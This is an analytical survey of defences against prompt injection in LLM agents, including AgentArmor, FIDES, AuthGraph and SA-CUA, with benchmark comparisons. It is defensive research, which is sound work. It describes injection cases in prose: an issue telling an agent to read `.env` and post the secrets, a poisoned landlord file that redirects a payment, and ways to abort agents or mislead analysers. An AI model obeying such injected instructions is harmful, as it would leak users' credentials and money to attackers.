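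*Intent-Conditioned Argument Mediation for Tool-Using LLM Agents* (2026) adds a condition for values that direct the agent's authority, such as a recipient. Such a value must have a permitted origin, and the user's intent must also authorise that particular value. This covers mistakes in which an agent puts a trusted value into the wrong argument without any attack. If the system can't work out the intent, it authorises only what the user wrote. The design has to trust the component that extracts the intent, and a mistake there could authorise the wrong recipient. Like PACT, it doesn't address attacks on the choice of tool.

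### What AgentArmor leaves open

Wang and colleagues give only one complete rule, the one for `create_trans`, and they don't propose a rule for the reminder. In their main description, the operator can write rules in advance and the system can generate them as it runs. In their limitations section, they acknowledge that the current rules are mostly predefined and adapt poorly when tasks change. They plan to have a language model generate rules and a formal validation engine check them.

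Predefined rules work well for tools that should behave the same way in every task, but poorly for email recipients, because the proper source of the address depends on the request. If the user types the address, it should come only from the user's prompt. If the user asks to send a reminder to an attendee, the address has to come from the calendar. A fixed rule that allows the calendar in both cases leaves the first task open to an attack through the calendar that a stricter rule would prevent.

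Wang and colleagues also don't specify whether a rule can override the edge check. Take the rule that the agent may send a file's contents only to a privileged group, and suppose the file has high confidentiality and the email tool accepts at most mid confidentiality. If the rule can't override the edge check, the check blocks the email whoever the recipient is, so the rule has no effect. If it can, the rule works as an exception that allows the agent to send the file to the privileged group.

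AgentArmor has one explicit setting for exceptions, which covers delegated instructions. If the operator allows them, AgentArmor trusts everything in a document that the user has told the agent to follow, including any instructions an attacker has added. Disallowing them catches more of these attacks but also blocks legitimate tasks. Wang and colleagues plan to add a check on whether the instructions fit the user's original request.

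### Endorsement and declassification

Information-flow control has two standard kinds of exception that limit label creep. Endorsement raises a value's integrity, and declassification lowers its confidentiality. For example, approving an attendee's address for use in a reminder is an endorsement, and telling a customer only the end date of a confidential contract is a declassification.

To grant exceptions safely, Seip and colleagues follow a principle called robust endorsement, which they credit to Zdancewic and Myers (2001) and Myers and colleagues (2006). The value under review may determine whether it passes the check, but it must not influence the check itself or the expected answer. Asking a second language model whether a value looks right breaks this principle, because the value could contain text that persuades the model to approve it.

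Their system, SA-CUA, which operates a computer through its screen, derives the expected answer from trusted sources without looking at the value. Ordinary code then compares the two. For an email recipient, the expected answer comes from the user's contact book. In the reminder example, the code would compare the address from the calendar with the contact book's entry for the attendee. An attacker could block the reminder by making the comparison fail, but couldn't have it sent to an address that differs from that entry.

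Seip and colleagues tested this on 78 tasks in which the attacker replaced a value with another of the same kind, such as a lookalike address or a malicious copy of a code repository. They used two models to run the agent:

| Model | Attack success, unprotected | Attack success, SA-CUA | Tasks completed under attack, unprotected | Tasks completed under attack, SA-CUA |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3.8-27B | 43.6% | 0% | 53.4% | 50.9% |
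| GPT-5.6-Luna | 38.5% | 0% | 60.3% | 69.2% |

The drop in task completion is clearer on ordinary tasks with no attack. On a set of 36, SA-CUA completed 30.6% with the first model and 38.9% with the second, while the unprotected agent completed 58.3% with either model. Many everyday decisions depend on information that no independent source can confirm. If a user asks an agent to buy a laptop in good condition, the only description of its condition may be the seller's.

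The agent should not be able to grant exceptions, because a hijacked agent would approve the attacker's values. The user can grant them for a task, and so can trusted code the operator has written. Asking the user is simple and flexible, but Seip and colleagues warn that people who see too many security prompts start approving them without checking.

The scope of each approval therefore matters. In *PerMIT* (2026), a design for protecting agents with long-term memory, a user's confirmation endorses one value for one tool, so approving an address for reminders doesn't approve it for payments. The approval lasts as long as the system keeps its local copy, which reduces the number of prompts. But the system might then not ask about that address again, even if a later message to it is far more sensitive than the reminder.

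PACT lets trusted procedures issue a certificate for a value that has failed a check. The certificate specifies the failure it excuses, the procedure that issued it, the argument roles it covers and the highest trust it can confer. An address approved as a recipient therefore can't become part of a command. The typed releases in Santos-Grueiro's CXI are similar endorsements, in which trusted code approves a value for one field.

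*The LLMbda Calculus* (2026), which defines a small formal language for agents, places two further limits on endorsement. If untrusted data led the program to the endorsement step, the result stays untrusted, so a malicious email can't make its contents trusted by getting the agent to request approval for them. Endorsement also can't lower confidentiality, so approving the attendee's address would not let the agent include a confidential agenda in the reminder.

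Including the agenda would require a separate declassification, which the user may not be the right person to grant. If the agenda belongs to the company, the company should decide who may see it. The decision also has to be safe from outside influence. A program that releases only the end date of a contract reveals a predictable amount, but if a stranger's email can determine which part of the contract the program releases, the stranger can make it release the price instead. SA-CUA handles endorsement carefully but does not guarantee confidentiality, so its agent could still post a secret on a public forum. AgentArmor tracks both confidentiality and integrity, but Wang and colleagues describe no procedure for declassifying data or for endorsing a single value.

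## AgentArmor's test results: attacks stopped, tasks lost, time spent

Wang and colleagues tested AgentArmor on AgentDojo, mainly with GPT-4o, a 2024 language model, as the agent. In the September 2025 version of their paper, AgentArmor reduces the attack success rate from 41% to 3%, while the share of tasks completed without an attack falls only from 73% to 72%. Every test they report shows a large reduction in successful attacks. The claim that AgentArmor barely reduces utility is much weaker, because the 73% and 72% may come from different models and the agent completes far fewer tasks when it is under attack.

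### How a run is scored

Besides attack success and utility, Wang and colleagues use two measures of detection:

true positive rate = attacks stopped / attacks that would have succeeded

false positive rate = harmless runs stopped / all harmless runs

The true positive rate ignores attacks that would have failed anyway. It therefore gives a simple estimate of the attack success rate that remains with the defence in place:

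remaining rate ≈ original rate × (1 − true positive rate)

With the September version's 93% average true positive rate, the estimate is 41% × 0.07, or about 2.9%, which agrees with the reported 3%.

Wang and colleagues don't use AgentDojo's check to decide whether an attack succeeded. *PromptArmor* (2025) explains that this check counts an attack as successful only if the agent completes every step. Suppose the attacker wants all unread emails forwarded. If the agent forwards all but one, or misspells the attacker's address, AgentDojo records a failed attack. If AgentArmor stopped such a run, AgentDojo's check would make it look like a false alarm, even though the agent was clearly following the attacker's instructions.

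The September version instead uses a language model as the judge. It reads the system prompt, the user's prompt, the injected prompt and the list of the agent's actions, and assigns one of four outcomes:

- the attack failed;
- the agent took only some of the actions the attacker wanted;
- the agent took all of them but with wrong parameters;
- the attack succeeded in full.

This is a sensible way to decide whether an alarm was justified. But it makes the results harder to compare with scores from AgentDojo's check, and the judge may misread a run.

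The paper's first version, from August 2025, gives two conflicting sets of results. Its table reports a true positive rate of 95.75% and a false positive rate of 3.66%, but its text reports about 82% and above 30%. According to the text, the false alarms were due partly to AgentDojo's strict check and partly to the dependency analyser, which often confused control and data dependencies when a user's request contained a condition. The two sets of figures may come from different stages of development, but the paper doesn't explain the difference.

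### Comparison with Progent, SecAlign and CaMeL

The September version compares AgentArmor with three leading defences. Progent checks each tool call against rules written in a small policy language, such as a rule that restricts a parameter to certain values. SecAlign retrains the model to follow legitimate instructions rather than injected ones. CaMeL fixes a plan before the agent reads untrusted data and restricts how information can flow through that plan.

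AgentArmor allowed 3% of attacks, slightly more than Progent at 2% and CaMeL at 0%, but it completed 72% of tasks, compared with 64% for Progent and 48% for CaMeL. Wang and colleagues attribute the higher completion rate to AgentArmor blocking only problematic data flows, whereas Progent's generated rules lack information about which instruction led to a call. SecAlign completed 76% of tasks, but it requires access to the model's weights, which rules it out for most commercial models. An operator with that access could use both SecAlign and AgentArmor.

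A later paper, *Aligning Provenance with Authorization* (2026), casts doubt on the comparison with Progent. Wang, Li and Tian tested the same three defences on both GPT-4o and the smaller GPT-4o-mini. Peiran Wang is also the first author of the AgentArmor paper. The table below sets the later paper's utility figures beside those in the AgentArmor paper. AgentArmor's row comes entirely from the AgentArmor paper, which also reports results for each model.

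| Defence | Utility in AgentArmor's comparison | Utility on GPT-4o-mini | Utility on GPT-4o |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 73% | 73% | 79% |
| SecAlign | 76% | 76% | 76% |
| Progent | 64% | 64% | 76% |
| CaMeL | 48% | 48% | 53% |
| AgentArmor | 72% | 76.3% | 71.8% |

The utilities for the other defences in AgentArmor's comparison are identical to the later paper's figures for GPT-4o-mini, but AgentArmor's 72% matches its result on GPT-4o. The undefended attack success rate of 41% also suggests GPT-4o, for which Wang, Li and Tian report 40%, compared with 17% for GPT-4o-mini. The comparison therefore seems to combine results from two models, although neither paper says so and the match could have another explanation.

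If the mixture is real, AgentArmor's ranking depends on the model. On GPT-4o-mini, it completes about 12 percentage points more tasks than Progent, with the same attack success rate of 2%. On GPT-4o, it completes about 4 points fewer than Progent and allows more attacks. AgentArmor would reduce utility on GPT-4o by about 7 points instead of 1, which is still moderate. CaMeL completes fewer tasks than AgentArmor on both models.

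In the later tests, defences that only change the prompt gave far less protection against the benchmark's attacks than any of the outside checks. On GPT-4o, the attack success rate was 25% with the user's request repeated and 23% with spotlighting, which marks outside text so that the model can recognise it. Repeating the request also raised utility to 84%, from 79% for the undefended agent.

Wang, Li and Tian did not retest AgentArmor itself. According to the September version of the AgentArmor paper, company policy restricted the code, and the team expected to release it by 30 September 2025. Among the results above, the comparison by Yao and colleagues comes closest to an outside test. They used AgentArmor to investigate past attacks and found many false attributions.

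Independent tests matter here because they often don't match the results a defence's developers report. *PromptArmor*, which uses a language model to find and remove injected text, reports an attack success rate below 1% on AgentDojo, but Wang, Li and Tian measured 7% with GPT-4o-mini and 8% with GPT-4o.

### Results by attack and by model

The September version also tests nine styles of injection. Some imitate an instruction from the user or developer, some use knowledge of the agent's tools, and some tell the agent to ignore its earlier instructions. Across the nine styles, AgentArmor reduced the attack success rate from 28% to 4% on average, with a false positive rate of 2.6%.

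AgentArmor did well against most attack styles. For injections that imitate an important instruction, the true positive rate was between 91% and 97%, even when the attacker got the user's or model's name wrong. Attacks that told the agent to ignore its instructions never succeeded with AgentArmor in place. The exception was the "direct" attack, which just states the attacker's request. AgentArmor detected only 40% of the direct attacks that would otherwise have succeeded, reducing the success rate from 4% to 2%. The 40% figure is based on few cases, since 4% of AgentDojo's 629 security cases is only about 25 successful attacks.

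All nine are fixed templates that don't target the dependency analyser. Narisetty's *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (2026) examined how defences outside the model withstand attackers who adapt to them. The results were consistent with the idea that fixed rules outside the model are harder to defeat than detectors that read the text, but didn't establish it. Even if the idea is right, AgentArmor would benefit only partly, because its rules apply to a graph that a language model infers.

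A third version of the AgentArmor paper, with a new title, reports the same 3% attack success rate on AgentDojo and 0% on ASB, another benchmark of attacks on agents. The ASB result makes it less likely that the design works only on AgentDojo's tasks, but it doesn't replace a test with adaptive attacks.

The September version gives these results for five models protected by AgentArmor:

| Model | Attack success rate | Utility without attack |
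|---|---|---|
| Claude 3.7 Sonnet | 0.03% | 87.0% |
| Gemini 2.0 Flash | 0.3% | 41.7% |
| GPT-4o | 5.2% | 71.8% |
| GPT-4o-mini | 2% | 76.3% |
| Llama 3.3 70B | 0.8% | 58.1% |

Wang and colleagues conclude that AgentArmor works best with stronger models that have robust safety training. The result for Claude fits this, but GPT-4o did worse than GPT-4o-mini on both measures. That difference probably comes from the models. If the undefended attack success rates were 40% for GPT-4o and 17% for GPT-4o-mini, as in the later paper, AgentArmor stopped about 87% and 88% of the attacks that would otherwise have succeeded. So more attacks seem to have got through on GPT-4o because it was more vulnerable without the defense.

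Some of the paper's figures are inconsistent. It gives the attack success rate with GPT-4o as 3%, 4% or 5.2% in different places, and the number of test cases as 629 in one place and more than 7,000 in another. The 0.03% for Claude can't come from 629 cases, since a single success would be 0.16%. It could represent two successes in about 7,000 cases, or it could be a misprint for 3%. AgentArmor stops most of these attacks whichever figures are correct, but differences of one or two percentage points between defences are weak evidence that one is better.

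All five models are also old by the standards of late 2026. The models that Zhou and colleagues tested resisted the standard attacks unaided. On models like those, this benchmark would show the tasks AgentArmor loses and the time it adds, but almost none of its benefits.

### Tasks lost when an attack is detected

AgentArmor aborts the whole run when it detects an attack, so the user's task fails along with the attacker's. The 72% figure is utility without attack, and the GPT-4o agent completes 48% of tasks when injections are present.

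The August version reports its results for each of AgentDojo's four settings, and they show where the losses fall:

| Setting | Attack success, undefended | Attack success, AgentArmor | Utility, undefended | Utility, AgentArmor | False positive rate |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace | 23.03% | 2.56% | 49.36% | 46.98% | 4.51% |
| Banking | 54.35% | 6.52% | 78.99% | 41.30% | 1.59% |
| Travel | 6.39% | 0.07% | 67.11% | 65.04% | 2.85% |
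| Slack | 78.43% | 1.96% | 65.69% | 11.76% | 13.64% |
| Overall | 16.66% | 1.16% | 63.48% | 56.78% | 3.66% |

Utility fell by 54 points in Slack and nearly 38 points in banking, although AgentArmor wrongly stopped only 13.64% of harmless runs in Slack and fewer than 2% in banking. These false alarms are too rare to explain the losses, so the utility figures probably include runs under attack, in which AgentArmor correctly detected an injection but also abandoned the user's task.

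Most of this doesn't show in the overall row. Its utility of 56.78% is higher than in three of the four settings, which is possible only if the fourth, travel, has more than half the weight. Attacks rarely succeeded in travel even without a defence. If all four settings count equally, utility falls from about 65% to 41%, a loss of 24 points instead of the 7 in the overall row.

An attacker can use these aborts to stop an agent's work, since an injection only has to make the agent attempt a forbidden call, even if the check blocks it. In the September tests, AgentArmor reduced successful attacks from 41 to 3 in every hundred, so it must have ended about 38 of every hundred attacked runs. A stranger could keep an agent from working through an inbox by sending it an injection that triggers an abort. The stranger might also stop the agent without fooling it, by writing text that the analyser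 wrongly blames for a legitimate call.

This differs from the denial-of-service attack that Wang and colleagues acknowledge, in which an injection causes the agent itself to stop. They plan to add an "end" action to the graph so that AgentArmor can check the agent's decision to stop, but this wouldn't help when AgentArmor ends the run.

An undefended agent also loses many tasks under attack, because a hijacked agent often neglects what the user asked for. Wang, Li and Tian report these figures for GPT-4o, and AgentArmor's own figures are in the last row:

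| Defence | Utility without attack | Utility under attack |
|---|---|---|
| None | 79% | 54% |
| SecAlign | 76% | 74% |
| Progent | 76% | 61% |
| CaMeL | 53% | 41% |
| PromptArmor | 71% | 21% |
| AgentArmor | 72% | 48% |

If the two sets of tests are comparable, an agent under attack completes slightly fewer tasks with AgentArmor (48%) than without it (54%). It is reasonable to accept that loss to prevent theft of money or data. But Progent and SecAlign both leave the user better off than having no defence, so security doesn't always require losing the task. CausalArmor, for example, removes the injected instructions and lets the agent choose again.

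The problem should be smaller with newer models, since a model that ignores an injection never attempts the forbidden call. It would remain for operators whose models are easy to hijack, and they need outside checks most.

### Instructions in a document the user trusts

Wang and colleagues reviewed AgentArmor's failures by hand and traced most of them to delegated instructions, which they call transfer execution. In their example, the user tells the agent to read `landlord-notices.txt` and follow its instructions precisely, but an attacker has added a command to the file. If the operator allows delegation, a payment to the attacker has the same high integrity as a change to the rent, so a rule based only on integrity must allow both.

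Delegation also explains the poor result on direct attacks. The direct injection uses no trick to make the agent obey, so it probably succeeds mainly where the user has already told the agent to obey the text, which AgentArmor then treats as trusted by default. More elaborate injections also get the agent to obey in ordinary tasks, where AgentArmor can trace the resulting tool call to an untrusted source and block it.

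Wang and colleagues compared allowing delegation with forbidding it, and each setting was better on two measures:

| Setting | Better results on |
|---|---|
| Delegation allowed | Utility, false positive rate |
| Delegation forbidden | True positive rate, attack success rate |

With the landlord's file, allowing delegation lets the attacker's payment through, while forbidding it stops the agent from changing the rent. The right setting depends on who can edit the documents that users tend to rely on. An operator could reasonably allow delegation to a company's internal manual but forbid it for email attachments, though AgentArmor's setting, as described, applies to all sources.

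Benchmarks can understate how many tasks the stricter choice loses. *The Landscape of Prompt Injection Threats* (2026), a survey that Peiran Wang also worked on, finds that many defences score well by suppressing information from the agent's context, then fail on realistic tasks that depend on that information. Wang, Li and Tian's results on AgentDyn, the benchmark in which agents must adapt to what they find, are consistent with this. With GPT-4o and no attack, Progent's utility was 76% on AgentDojo but 7% on AgentDyn, and CaMeL's fell from 53% to zero. The undefended agent completed 53% of AgentDyn's tasks. AgentDyn appeared in 2026, after AgentArmor's September tests, but a version of AgentArmor that forbade delegation might also do badly on it.

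Wang and colleagues plan to add a check on whether an instruction fits the user's request. It would probably catch an instruction in the landlord's file to forward an address book, but it would help much less against an instruction to pay the rent into a different account, because that fits the request. To catch that, the system would need independent evidence of the landlord's account number.

### AuthGraph

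The later paper presents a new defence, AuthGraph, to address the risk that injected text misleads the model that builds AgentArmor's graph. Wang, Li and Tian point out that AgentArmor has no independent graph to compare this one with.

AuthGraph therefore builds two graphs and compares them. The first describes what the agent did, and its builder reads everything, including any injection. The second describes what the agent is allowed to do. A separate model, the planner, builds it from only the user's request and the list of tools, before any tool returns a result, so an injection in those results can't influence it.

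In the paper's example, a user asks an agent to book a flight and a hotel. The planner specifies that the flight number must come from the flight search. A malicious hotel listing tells the agent to book flight `EVIL-123` and to open a web page to verify the booking. AuthGraph blocks the web page because opening it is unrelated to the task. It blocks the flight because `EVIL-123` doesn't appear in the flight search results. For this check, it searches the original tool output, so a false edge in the first graph can't hide where the number came from.

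On AgentDojo with GPT-4o, AuthGraph reduced the attack success rate from 40% to 1% and completed 76% of tasks. Removing the comparison's check on tool names raised the attack success rate to 21%, and removing its check on parameter sources raised it to 18%. On AgentDyn, AuthGraph completed 51% of tasks with an attack success rate of 2%, far better than Progent or CaMeL.

These results suggest that an independent plan is a better basis for judging a call than AgentArmor's single graph, but they don't show that AuthGraph solves the landlord problem. Wang, Li and Tian exclude delegated instructions from its scope, reasoning that the user chose to trust the document. Since delegation caused most of AgentArmor's failures, AuthGraph's 1% and AgentArmor's 3% may not cover the same attacks.

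When a task depends on what the agent finds, the planner can mark a step where it will plan again after reading the tool's output. It must list the permitted tools in advance, and ordinary code enforces the list. In the landlord example, the list might include changing a scheduled payment but not sending email. An attacker who controls the file could still misuse the permitted tools. AuthGraph also uses a language model for some of its comparisons, including judging whether an unexpected tool call is harmless, and injected text may be able to target that model too.

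### Time and tokens

With AgentArmor, an average run took 20.89 seconds in the September tests. Building the graph took about 14.5 seconds (69.6%) of that, because it requires repeated calls to a language model. Checking the types took only 1.13 seconds. The remaining 5.2 seconds or so were presumably the agent's own work. If so, AgentArmor made runs take about four times as long. Building the graph also used 13,609 tokens, 72% of the run's total of about 18,900.

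Wang and colleagues measured 11.24 seconds for Progent and 46.72 for CaMeL. Wang, Li and Tian found similar times for both and measured 5.32 seconds for an undefended agent:

| Defence | AgentArmor's tests | Later tests |
|---|---|---|
| None | – | 5.32 s |
| Progent | 11.24 s | 8.54 s |
| AuthGraph | – | 9.93 s |
| AgentArmor | 20.89 s | – |
| CaMeL | 46.72 s | 48.97 s |

AuthGraph is about twice as fast as AgentArmor but uses more than twice as many tokens, at 47,400 per task. The token counts may not be directly comparable, because the undefended agent in the later tests already used 11,200.

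A delay of 15 seconds hardly matters when an agent works in the background, but it would be irritating in a conversation. Longer tasks would suffer more. Before each call, the analyser reads the observations from all the earlier ones. If each observation has *k* tokens, then over *n* calls it reads

k · n(n − 1) / 2

tokens of observations. For 5 calls this is 10*k*, and for 20 calls it is 190*k*, so four times as many calls require 19 times as much reading. The agent itself rereads its context in much the same way, so AgentArmor's share of the total needn't rise, but the extra seconds and tokens would. A smaller or faster analyser would reduce both, at the risk of more wrong edges. An operator could also run the analyser only before sensitive calls, as CausalArmor does with its own test, since reading a calendar rarely needs the same scrutiny as sending money.

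## Carrying labels while the agent runs

Most of AgentArmor's time overhead comes from asking a language model which inputs caused each tool call. A system can avoid this step by assuming that everything the model has read influenced its next call. Ordinary code can then label each piece of data as it arrives, combine the labels when data is mixed, and check the resulting label before a tool runs. This removes the language-model analyser that an attacker could mislead, but it causes label creep, because one untrusted input affects the label on every later call. The main systems of this kind therefore try to keep untrusted text out of the model's context.

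### f-secure

*System-Level Defense against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks* (Wu, Cecchetti and Xiao, 2024) describes an early version called f-secure, which splits the agent into three parts. The planner, a language model, chooses one step at a time. The executor, which is ordinary code, runs each step by calling a tool or a second language model. The security monitor, also ordinary code, controls which results the planner may see.

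In one example, a user asks the agent to read emails about company budgets and notify the manager if any budget exceeds $1,000. The search returns two emails from colleagues, with budgets of $724 and $1,024, and one from an attacker telling the agent to forward the budgets. The monitor labels each email by its sender and passes only the colleagues' emails to the planner. The planner then notifies the manager without having read the attacker's instruction.

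The planner can also use a result it hasn't seen, because each step refers to its inputs by number and the executor loads the contents. Suppose the user wants the agent to append an outside medical study to a clinic's notes and email the combined file to a doctor. The combined file inherits the study's untrusted label, so the monitor hides it from the planner. The planner can still specify a step that emails "the output of step 1".

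Wu and colleagues prove a property close to noninterference. If two collections of data, Q₁ and Q₂, differ only in their untrusted parts, any sequence of steps π is equally likely with either:

Pr[π | q, Q₁] = Pr[π | q, Q₂]

Here *q* is the user's request. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* argues that in practice f-secure still lets untrusted data influence the plan indirectly. This may happen, for example, when a step fails, because the planner then generates a replacement. An attacker whose data makes a tool fail could therefore change what the agent does next.

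On InjecAgent, no attack succeeded against f-secure with any of four models, while 17% to 52% succeeded against an ordinary agent in the benchmark's basic setting. Wu and colleagues treated every tool output in this test as untrusted, so no injection reached the planner, and the zero success rate follows almost directly from the design. They measured task completion on separate benchmarks, which gives little idea of how often the planner would need text withheld from it. The monitor's checks took less than a millisecond per step, compared with one to three seconds for the model to generate the step.

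### The context label in FIDES

FIDES, which Microsoft researchers present in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, adds confidentiality to this scheme and lets the agent ask questions about the data it can't see. Its simplest form keeps a single label for the whole conversation:

1. The context starts with the label of the system prompt and the user's request, normally trusted and public.
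2. When a message *m* arrives, code joins its label to the context label *L*, so that L ← L ⊔ ℓ(m).
3. When the model generates a tool call, the call and all its arguments inherit *L*.
4. Code checks the call against a policy and runs the tool only if it passes.
5. The tool's result receives the join of the labels on the call, its arguments and any data the tool read.

The paper gives two basic policies. Under the first, a call with real consequences, such as a payment, may run only if the call and its arguments are trusted. Under the second, a call may send information only to people who have permission to read it. The second policy can't prevent an injection from causing a call, but it limits what the call can disclose.

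These checks can work even if the model doesn't notice an attack, but they need correct labels. They restrict direct flows of data, though an observer could still learn something from the agent's choice of tools.

### Hiding results in variables

The full version of FIDES limits label creep by hiding data that would change the context label. When a tool returns a result, code compares each field's label with the context label. If the field's label is no more restrictive, the code leaves the field visible. Otherwise it stores the value in memory, outside the model's context, and shows the model only a variable name.

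Suppose a user asks the agent to send the three latest emails to a colleague on Slack. The email tool returns text from strangers, which FIDES stores under the name `#read_emails_0`. The model then generates a call that sends `#read_emails_0` to the colleague, and code inserts the emails just before the call runs. The context has stayed trusted, so the choice of tool and the recipient are trusted, and only the message body is untrusted.

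AgentArmor also distinguishes a call from its parameters, but has to infer the distinction after the model has read everything. In FIDES, the emails cannot have influenced the choice of tool because the model never saw them. An operator can then require a trusted recipient while accepting an untrusted message body.

### The quarantined model

If the user wants a summary of the emails, FIDES has a second language model, with no access to tools, read them. The programmer Simon Willison proposed this arrangement, known as the dual LLM pattern, in 2023. The main model sends the quarantined model a question and the name of a variable. FIDES stores the answer in another variable, whose label joins the labels of everything used to produce the answer.

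An injection in the emails can still corrupt the quarantined model's answer, for instance by making the summary empty, but that model can't call tools. If the agent passes the answer to a tool as an argument, the policy must either accept or reject that argument.

Some tasks require the main model to learn something from untrusted data before it can choose the next step. In one example, a user asks the agent to book a particular hotel if its rating is higher than 4. The main model could read the reviews directly, but its context would then become untrusted. FIDES also lets the model ask a narrower question whose answer has a fixed form, such as yes or no. The label on the answer records this form, and a policy can allow a yes-or-no answer from an untrusted source to influence a booking.

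An answer with *k* possible values carries at most log₂ k bits, so a yes-or-no answer carries at most one bit and a choice among four options at most two. Someone who tampers with the rating could decide whether the agent books this hotel, but couldn't use that one bit to make it email a stranger. This is a form of endorsement in which the size of the answer limits the damage.

The limit applies to each answer separately. Joining two yes-or-no labels gives another yes-or-no label, so twenty answers could carry 20 bits in total while their combined label still indicated one bit. A careful policy would also have to limit the number of questions. The researchers did not include fixed answer forms in their tests, so their results don't show how well this part of the design works.

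### FIDES on AgentDojo

The researchers tested FIDES on AgentDojo, using an attack that names the agent's own tools. AgentDojo has no security labels, so they marked a field as untrusted if any of the benchmark's injections targets it. For example, if any injection used an email body, they treated every email body as untrusted. An operator doesn't know in advance which fields attackers will use, so the results show how FIDES performs when its labels cover every attack.

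With GPT-4o and no defence, 152 injections succeeded. Hiding data in variables reduced this to 21 with no policy in force, and adding the policies reduced it to zero. AgentDojo's own check recorded three successes against the full system, but the researchers reviewed them and judged that none was a real injection. They excluded cases in which the policy had blocked the call or permitted the action, or the injection only changed the wording of an answer. Zero therefore means that no attack violated the policy, which is a weaker result than no attacker getting anything they wanted.

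The policies were also looser than the basic ones. For payments, bookings and many other actions, they checked only whether the choice of tool was trusted and ignored the labels on the arguments. As with the planted address in the meeting reminder, an attacker could change the account number on a bill the user asked the agent to pay, and the payment would go through.

The table gives the share of tasks completed when there was no attack. The last column gives the share that the researchers judged possible without showing the main model any untrusted text. The averages weight the four suites equally.

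| Suite | No defence, GPT-4o | Context label only, GPT-4o | FIDES, GPT-4o | FIDES, o1 | Possible in principle |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace | 75.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% | 64.5% | 95.0% |
| Travel | 70.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% | 68.0% | 90.0% |
| Banking | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% | 56.2% | 56.2% |
| Slack | 93.3% | 20.0% | 47.6% | 54.3% | 57.1% |
| Average | 84.3% | 41.9% | 50.0% | 60.8% | 74.6% |

The paper highlights that FIDES completes more tasks than the simpler design, an agent with a context label and the same policies. The gain is 8 percentage points with GPT-4o and 16 with o1, OpenAI's reasoning model from 2024. Compared with an undefended agent, FIDES's completion rate is about 34 points lower with GPT-4o and 23 points lower with o1. The paper's smaller figure of a 6.3% loss is for o1 with the policies switched off.

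Some of this loss comes from the model. GPT-4o often confused variable names or failed to query the quarantined model when it should have, and o1 used both variables and the quarantined model better. A current model would presumably improve on o1 in the workspace and travel suites, where o1 remained well below what is possible in principle. In banking and Slack, o1 was already near that limit. Many banking tasks require the agent to read a file and follow its instructions, which makes the context untrusted, so the policy blocks the payment. A better model can't fix this without an exception to the policy. Such delegated instructions also caused most of AgentArmor's failures.

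FIDES keeps working under attack. When a policy blocks a call, it reports the violation to the model as if it were a tool's result, so the agent can try something else. With GPT-4o, average task completion was about 50% both with and without attacks. AgentArmor, which aborts the whole run, did better without attacks but slightly worse under attack. The FIDES evaluation didn't include measurements of time or token use, although each question to the quarantined model adds to both.

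### The release in Microsoft's Agent Framework

In May 2026, Microsoft added an experimental version of FIDES to Agent Framework, its toolkit for building agents. Its announcement, *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026), uses the example of an agent that sorts the issues people report on a GitHub repository. The agent can read issues, post public comments, and read and write files. An attacker opens an issue that looks like an ordinary bug report but ends with an instruction to read `.env`, a file where developers often keep passwords, and post its contents as a comment.

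The labels change as the run proceeds:

| Call | Context before the call | Outcome |
|---|---|---|
| `read_issue` | Trusted, public | Runs and returns untrusted, public text |
| `read_file(".env")` | Untrusted, public | Runs and returns private text |
| `post_comment` | Untrusted, private | Blocked, because a comment may contain only public data |
| `write_file`, if the attacker asks for it | Untrusted | Blocked, because this tool doesn't accept untrusted input |

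The developer can have the framework ask for human approval instead of blocking an action. By default, the framework hides untrusted results in variables and uses the quarantined model to process them. In this example, the developer has switched off automatic hiding, so the main model reads the malicious issue in full and the policy alone stops the leak.

The announcement is inconsistent about `post_comment`. According to one sentence, FIDES blocks the tool while any untrusted content remains in the context. But the code sets only a confidentiality limit, the tool's description mentions only private context, and the step-by-step account attributes the block to private data. One setting in the code lists `read_issue` as allowed to run in an untrusted context, which might imply that unlisted tools can't, but `read_file` is also unlisted and runs after the agent has read the malicious issue.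 In the example's configuration, then, only private content appears to block `post_comment`.

The example doesn't discuss that an injection could still make the agent post a link to a malicious download under the project's name, since the link is public text. The developer could prevent this by making `post_comment` reject untrusted input, but then the agent couldn't comment on any issue it had read without a person's approval. With automatic hiding on, the context could stay trusted, but the comment might still contain text from the issue.

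Microsoft lists several limits, including that labels are optional and that the framework treats the output of an unlabelled tool as trusted and public. If a developer adds a web search and forgets the label, an injection in a search result counts as trusted and can reach `write_file`. AgentArmor, by contrast, gives unlabelled data low integrity by default. Microsoft is asking developers whether it should adopt a stricter default.

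Another limit is that once an untrusted item enters the context, the rest of the run is untrusted unless the developer explicitly removes the item. The quarantined model can also answer only one question at a time, without follow-ups.

### Label creep in five steps

A small invented example shows how quickly one context label can stop legitimate work. A café manager asks an agent to check tomorrow's weather, open the staff rota, send the rota to the staff, post opening hours of 9 to 5 on the café's website, and pay the window cleaner 80 euros. Payments require a trusted context, website posts require a public one, and messages may contain private data if every recipient has permission to read it. The model reads each result directly:

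| Step | Call | Context before the call | Outcome |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Look up the weather on the web | Trusted, public | Allowed |
| 2 | Open the staff rota | Untrusted, public | Allowed |
| 3 | Send the rota to the staff | Untrusted, private | Allowed |
| 4 | Post the opening hours | Untrusted, private | Blocked, context is private |
| 5 | Pay the window cleaner | Untrusted, private | Blocked, context is untrusted |

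The manager specified the opening hours and the payment in full, and neither depends on the weather or the rota.

If the agent posted the hours and made the payment first, all five calls would go through. A planner that took labels into account could find this order, as *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* suggests. FIDES could also keep the original order by storing the weather and the rota in variables, since the agent can send the rota without reading it.

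Neither solution is enough if the manager wants to cancel the window cleaner when rain is likely, because the agent must then learn something from an untrusted page before it acts. With FIDES, the agent could ask a yes-or-no question, but many tasks need a longer answer. The other proposed remedies try to loosen the labels after the model has read the data. AgentArmor, for example, infers narrower dependencies, but this brings back the risk of missed edges.

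Microsoft is considering labels that apply to individual messages, and labels that weaken when the framework compacts a long conversation. Weakening labels this way would need care, because the summary could preserve an attacker's instruction after the original text is gone.

### Graded labels

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* proposes replacing all-or-nothing labels with estimates of how much information an output carries about each source. This draws on a field called quantitative information flow. One common measure of the information an output *O* carries about a source *S* is

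I(S; O) = H(S) − H(S | O)

where *H* is uncertainty in bits. If the agent would pay the window cleaner 80 euros whatever the weather page contained, the payment carries no information about the page, and the system could treat it as trusted.

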